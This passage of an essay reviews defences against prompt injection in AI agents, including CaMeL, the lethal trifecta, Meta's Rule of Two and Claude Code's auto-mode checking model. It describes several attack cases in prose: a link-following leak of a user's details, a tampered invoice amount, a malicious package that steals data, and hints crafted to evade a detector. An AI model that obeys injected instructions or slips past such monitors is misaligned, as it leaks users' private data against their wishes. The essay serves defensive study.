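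This protects the LLM from instructions in the database but not from a malicious user, who can still ask for harmful code. So the code has to run in a sandbox, and even then private data could leak through the analysis. Asking the user to approve every step would be impractical, because the number of approvals would grow with every query and revision.

The email assistant can usually choose its next step from the request, but the SQL agent needs to see the last result first. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) makes the same point about software engineering, where an agent has to explore the code, run it, look at the errors and revise its theory of the bug. In the paper's tests, OpenAI's GPT-5.2 fixed 61.2 per cent of bugs with no defence, and none when the agent with the tools could get no information from the bug report.

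### How much can an attacker do with 30 characters?

A coding agent often needs information from documentation written by strangers. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest having a quarantined LLM convert the documentation into a strictly formatted description of the available functions, with names limited to, say, 30 characters. They think an injection is unlikely to survive the conversion.

Willison wondered whether the limit was safe. He imagined a function named `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance()`, after `rm -rf`, the Unix command that deletes a folder and everything in it. The name has 29 characters without the brackets. His example shows only that a dangerous suggestion can fit within the limit, and a good model might well ignore it. But Willison was right to notice that "unlikely" is a weaker standard than the guiding principle's "impossible".

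Hu and colleagues later tested short messages, though not ones this short. In their design, one agent reads the untrusted bug report and passes hints of at most 100 characters to a second agent, which has the tools. The second agent's prompt warns it about the hints, and an AI detector screens each one. The researchers used an automated attacker to write malicious hints, then planted them in bug reports with an order to copy them word for word. In a separate test of that step, the first agent always obeyed. The whole attack succeeded on 11 of 232 bugs, or 4.7 per cent. It never succeeded when they reran those 11 cases five times each, so the original successes seem to have been partly luck. The risk also grew as they raised the limit from 50 to 200 characters. A tighter limit probably helps, but these results give no reason to think that any particular length is safe.

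The alternative is to allow no free text. The bug-fixing agent built by Jacob and colleagues receives only numbers and fixed choices. In their tests, also with GPT-5.2, no attacks succeeded, compared with 98.9 per cent against the undefended agent, but the share of bugs fixed fell from 68.3 to 45.0 per cent. The agent that received 100-character hints fixed 62.5 per cent, about as many as its undefended version. The two studies used different selections of bugs, so the figures are not strictly comparable, but the short hints seem to preserve much more usefulness, though without the guarantee that comes from excluding free text.

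### An unpopular trade-off

Willison trusted the design patterns paper largely because Beurer-Kellner and colleagues admitted that their proposed agents cannot perform arbitrary tasks. Companies want to sell agents that can do anything. Willison called the restriction "not a popular trade-off" but said that admitting it gave the paper a lot of credibility. He had no complete solution to offer either, and one of the six patterns was his own. In a note the same day, Willison (2025) also praised the paper's clear writing and its usefulness to software developers.

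Willison was more critical of Google two days later. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) lists questions for developers, including whether an agent can clearly distinguish trusted user inputs from untrusted ones, and recommends clearly separating the parts of a prompt. In *An Introduction to Google's Approach to AI Agent Security* (2025), Willison objected that unambiguous separation is not possible and that the wording "implies a solution that does not exist".

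Díaz and colleagues admit on the same page that current LLMs do not rigorously separate the parts of a prompt, and Willison acknowledged this. Their question has a better answer for a whole system than for a single model, because ordinary software can track which text came from the user, as it does in CaMeL, which Kern also worked on. Willison's criticism applies more directly to the advice about prompts, since models do not reliably respect marks that separate one part from another.

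He was also doubtful about Google's proposal that an agent's permissions should change with its task. He could only think of having another AI adjust them, and an injection might influence that AI. The design patterns paper mentions a simple alternative, in which the LLM chooses the tools it needs based only on the user's request, before it reads anything untrusted, and the software then disables the rest.

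The first of the two layers of defence in Google's plan is a policy engine, ordinary software that checks each action against rules. It might block any purchase over $500 and require the user to confirm those between $100 and $500. Willison liked this, partly because it requires the user's approval only for risky actions. He also liked the idea of blocking external email just after the agent has read something from a suspicious source, which resembles CaMeL's tracking of untrusted data.

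The second layer uses AI models to recognise attacks. Willison had trouble seeing why a defence without guarantees was worth adding. Díaz and colleagues agree that it is inadequate on its own, but argue that fixed rules miss context. If an agent sends an email after reading a document, the user may have wanted that or it may be theft, and a simple rule cannot distinguish the two cases.

The adaptive attacks Willison reported that November support his refusal to rely on such defences, but they do not show that adding the second layer is useless. Hu and colleagues found that the prompt warning and the AI detector each made their agent harder to attack through short hints, and that using both worked best. Such a detector could also catch some of the corrupted messages that a fixed plan allows an agent to send.

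## How much usefulness do these designs cost, and has Willison's view held up?

Willison admired CaMeL but worried about its security policies, which somebody has to write and keep up to date. CaMeL relies on users for some of this work. In his April 2025 post, Willison said that anything requiring end users to think about security policies made him "deeply nervous". He had worked in application security for two decades and still hadn't fully figured out AWS IAM, Amazon's system for managing cloud permissions.

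CaMeL can also ask the user when a policy doesn't settle a case, which brings back the approval fatigue that Willison had worried about in 2023. He noted that even careful people can lapse, as the security researcher Troy Hunt had the month before, when he fell for a phishing email while jet-lagged. A Hacker News commenter added that many users wouldn't notice `bob@mycumpany.com` in place of `bob@mycompany.com`, and that there is nobody to ask when a task runs in the background.

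The same commenter asked whether all this limited an agent's usefulness. "I think it limits the usefulness a lot," Willison replied. He still thought it was the best option anyone had offered in two and a half years for building agents that don't leak private data to anyone who asks for it. He hoped for a version with well-chosen default policies and a clear interface.

### The lethal trifecta

Developers can build an application around CaMeL or one of the six patterns, but many people assemble their own agents from tools made by different suppliers. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect tools to LLMs, makes this easy. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warned that neither paper was any help to these users. They could stay safe only by never giving one agent the whole of what he called the lethal trifecta:

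- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- a way to communicate externally that could carry stolen data

A theft like the one planned against Marvin needs all three, so it fails if any of them is missing.

Users can easily end up with all three. GitHub's official MCP tool had them on its own. It could read bug reports that strangers had filed on public projects, read the user's private code, and publish that code in a pull request (a proposed change to a project). Willison listed more than a dozen products in which researchers had found similar holes since 2023. The suppliers fixed almost all of these holes promptly, usually by blocking the way the data got out, but no supplier can do that for a combination of tools a user has put together.

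Willison's rule is that an agent should not combine access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. This is cruder than CaMeL, which lets an agent have all three and controls what passes between them. Following the rule means giving up every task that needs all three, including using private files to answer a stranger's email.

### Putting numbers on "a lot"

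Willison never measured how much usefulness CaMeL costs. Two studies from November 2026 did, and both found a large loss.

In *The Devil is in the Context*, Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026) tested kinds of attack that existing benchmarks mostly miss. They took all 40 user tasks from the part of AgentDojo that simulates office work, paired each with a randomly chosen attack, and had an LLM rewrite the attack. Each rewritten attack took effect only under a stated condition, concerned the same subject as the user's task, and changed the content of an action or answer without adding an action. For example, an injection might make the agent report a $500 invoice as $50. A fixed plan gives little protection against these attacks because they can succeed without changing it.

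The agent ran on GPT-5.6-Luna, one of OpenAI's cheaper models. With no defence, it completed all 40 tasks under the original attacks and none of those attacks worked, but seven of the rewritten attacks succeeded. With CaMeL, one rewritten attack succeeded (2.5 per cent), but the agent completed 27.5 per cent of the users' tasks. With PromptArmor, which has an LLM find and delete injected instructions before the agent reads them, three attacks succeeded (7.5 per cent) and the agent completed 90 per cent of the tasks.

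On these figures, CaMeL stopped two more attacks than PromptArmor but lost most of the agent's usefulness. The difference of two attacks in 40 could easily be chance, unlike the gap between 11 and 36 completed tasks. CaMeL's lower attack rate may also be partly because an agent that fails at most of its tasks will fail at some of the attacker's too.

But Chang and colleagues wrote their attacks in advance and didn't adapt them to each defence, which favours a filter like PromptArmor. *The Attacker Moves Second* concluded that fixed attacks are almost useless for testing defences. As Willison reported, its 500 human attackers, competing for $20,000 in prizes, got past every defence. A determined attacker could probably beat PromptArmor more than 7.5 per cent of the time.

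In *CapLite*, Xu, Liu and Nakayama (2026) ran a much larger test on 15 freely downloadable models. Most were small models that people might run on their own machines, and 13 had between 1.7 and 12 billion parameters. Each model faced 929 attacks from AgentDojo, for a total of 13,935. In Progent, the rule-checking system, the agent's own model wrote the rules. CapLite is the researchers' own design.

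| Defence | Successful attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Tokens per run |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 2,322 | 50.2% | 28,000 |
| Progent | 676 | 40.6% | 63,400 |
| CaMeL | 20 | 27.2% | 93,700 |
| CapLite | 0 | 29.0% | 17,100 |

CaMeL's security held up well, and 17 of the 20 successful attacks were on a single model. Its programs were less reliable, and on eight of the 15 models more than 15 per cent of runs ended without a working program. The figure was 68 per cent on IBM's Granite-4.2-8B, because the model returned no code. CaMeL gives the model up to ten chances to repair a faulty program, and each attempt uses more tokens.

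Better programs can reduce the loss of usefulness. Among Google's Gemma 4 models, the smallest failed to produce a working program in 22.9 per cent of runs, compared with 3.3 per cent for the largest. With CaMeL, the largest completed 55.5 per cent of tasks under attack, compared with 63.4 per cent without a defence. But Xu and colleagues found no significant relationship between capability and the loss across all 15 models, and the biggest of them still dropped from 77.9 to 47.5 per cent. The two strongest commercial models in the multi-agent study kept most of their usefulness, though with the security policies switched off.

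Willison's "a lot" therefore fairly describes the loss for small and cheap models, but may be too pessimistic for the best ones. Chang and colleagues' office tasks also resemble the work of the email assistant, which the design patterns paper predicted would lose little usefulness. That prediction was badly wrong, at least for CaMeL on a cheap model.

Nobody has to write policies for CapLite. Ordinary code sorts the tools by the words in their names and descriptions, so "get" or "search" marks a tool that only reads, and "send" or "pay" marks one that acts. Before any action, the code checks that the recipient, amount or other target appears in the user's own request. If Bob's address appears only in an email, CapLite has to ask the user. An injection can still change the wording of a message or the time of a meeting.

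The check itself causes only a fairly small loss of usefulness. When Xu and colleagues removed it on eight of the models, the share of tasks completed when there was no attack rose by 5.6 percentage points, and 106 of 7,432 attacks succeeded. Most of CapLite's loss came from small models planning badly, often by leaving out an action the task needed. This is some evidence that the default policies Willison hoped for are possible, although the researchers tested their own system on only one benchmark.

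### Simpler limits

In the autumn of 2025, Willison found a rule that he could recommend to developers straight away. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) proposes that, until someone can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate externally.

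An agent that needs all three should work under human supervision or some other reliable check. In Meta's example, an email assistant could read only messages from trusted senders, work without sensitive data, or have a person approve any draft not addressed to a trusted recipient.

The rule builds on Willison's trifecta, which covers only data theft. It adds the ability to change things, so it also covers attacks that delete files or spend money. Willison called it the "best practical advice" for building secure agents while no defence was reliable. Meta's diagram marked an agent as "safe" if it read untrusted input and could change things but had no private data. Willison soon pointed out that such an agent could still do harm, and that an exception for this case would make the rule less simple.

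Like CaMeL, the Rule of Two relies on human approval for many of the tasks people most want done. This is a weakness because, as Meta acknowledges, a user may blindly confirm a warning.

In June 2026 OpenAI released Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, which restricts the network requests that a prompt injection could use to send data out. An injection can still reach ChatGPT and make its answers wrong. Willison said the mode looked "really good". He thought the external channel was by far the easiest part of the trifecta to restrict without making a system much less useful, and Lockdown Mode restricts it with fixed rules that an attacker can't persuade the system to ignore. He also concluded that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined data thief. Lockdown Mode is for people at unusual risk, and OpenAI's head of security, Dane Stuckey, said it was "not meant for everyone"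 because it sacrifices some functionality.

Fixed rules can have gaps too. Anthropic let its Claude chatbot open only web addresses that the user had typed or that a search had returned, so that an injection could not add stolen data to an address. This design had impressed Willison, but Claude could also follow links on pages it had already opened. In July 2026 he described how Ayush Paul had exploited this with a website that had a link for each letter of the alphabet. Claude followed the links to spell out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic has since stopped Claude from following such links. A developer who learns of a gap like this can close it completely, but it is much harder to eliminate a model's occasional bad judgement.

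### Still no convincing CaMeL

CaMeL has been slow to reach users. In January 2026, ten months after the paper, Willison still called it the most promising route he had seen to a safe personal assistant, but he had not seen a "convincing implementation" (*Moltbook is the most interesting place on the internet right now*, 2026).

Willison was writing about OpenClaw, an open source assistant that people were already connecting to their private email without waiting for a safe version. Some had bought a separate computer to run it, which protects their main machine but not their messages. One user had bought a car by having it negotiate with several dealers over email. Willison had not been brave enough to install it himself, and expected people to take bigger and bigger risks until something terrible happened.

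Google's Chrome browser may have the closest thing to a deployment of these designs. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a "User Alignment Critic", partly inspired by CaMeL and the Dual LLM pattern. This second model approves or vetoes each action the browser's agent proposes. It sees only a description of the action, never the raw web page, so an attacker cannot give it instructions directly.

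Chrome's design resembles CaMeL only to a limited extent. Its planning model reads untrusted pages, which CaMeL's privileged LLM never does, and its critic is another AI making a judgement, whereas CaMeL uses code to check tags. Chrome does add some fixed rules, such as restricting addresses written by the model to known public ones and asking the user before the agent visits a banking site.

*Inside the lethal trifecta*, from the security company Sophos, agrees with Willison that no production-grade version of CaMeL exists. He does not seem to have named one since January.

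### A model as the guard

The AI-based defences that Willison distrusts have become much better, and the clearest example is auto mode in Claude Code. In auto mode, a separate model checks whether each action fits the user's request, instead of the user having to approve it. When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026, Willison was "unconvinced". He wanted coding agents to run in a sandbox, with fixed rules limiting their access to files and the network.

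In August, Anthropic made auto mode the default for most individual and team plans. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) presents the evidence for this decision, starting with an experiment on human reviewers. Each of 1,053 paid testers worked through a coding session in which one approval request showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 per cent refused it, while auto mode blocked 89 per cent of the same commands.

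The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than real users, but Anthropic also found that real users approve 97 per cent of such requests. Willison accepted that auto mode was better than constant approvals, and the experiment supports his warnings about fatigue. The testers refused about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more requests. These results also count against the designs he prefers, because both CaMeL and the Rule of Two can end up asking the user. A well-configured CaMeL would ask much less often, which should help, but even early in a session the testers approved most of the dangerous commands.

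Anthropic's second piece of evidence is an evaluation by the company Trajectory Labs, which ran 72 attack scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 injection attempts succeeded against Anthropic's newest models, while 5.83 per cent succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, running in OpenAI's coding agent with a similar automatic reviewer.

With auto mode off, only 0.09 per cent of attacks on the same Claude models succeeded on average, so nearly all of the resistance came from the models themselves. That rate is about a tenth of the 1 per cent that Willison used to call a failing grade, and it is hard to reconcile with the view that training models to resist injections achieves little. Willison had already conceded in June that the labs' training seemed to be making attacks much harder.

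The test was easier than a real attack in one important way, because Trajectory Labs had optimised its attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and did not adapt them to the models it was testing. The checking model also does worse against attacks designed to get past it. When Apollo Research, an AI safety company, created such attacks in a separate exercise, the checking model missed 12 per cent of them, and it still missed 7 per cent after Anthropic had strengthened it. Anthropic says that auto mode does not eliminate risk, and recommends that people review high-stakes changes themselves.

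In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) wanted independent confirmation and also worried about attacks that look like ordinary work. A malicious software package might include instructions for the agent to download files before running the tests, using a program that actually steals data. He wasn't sure how any version of auto mode could prevent this. The episode made him want to work harder on running agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

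Later that month Willison shared a report of an attack that usually got past auto mode. He then added a correction that the attack was not classic prompt injection, because the model never followed malicious instructions from the website.

Willison has kept working on hard limits. In November 2026, in *59 posts tagged "sandboxing"*, he described "external sandboxes", which he had developed with the research lab Prime Radiant. The code an agent writes runs inside a sandbox, while the agent stays outside. This can contain the damage from an injection that no model detects, but only for code that runs in the sandbox. An assistant that has to read its user's email and reply to strangers still needs the whole trifecta.
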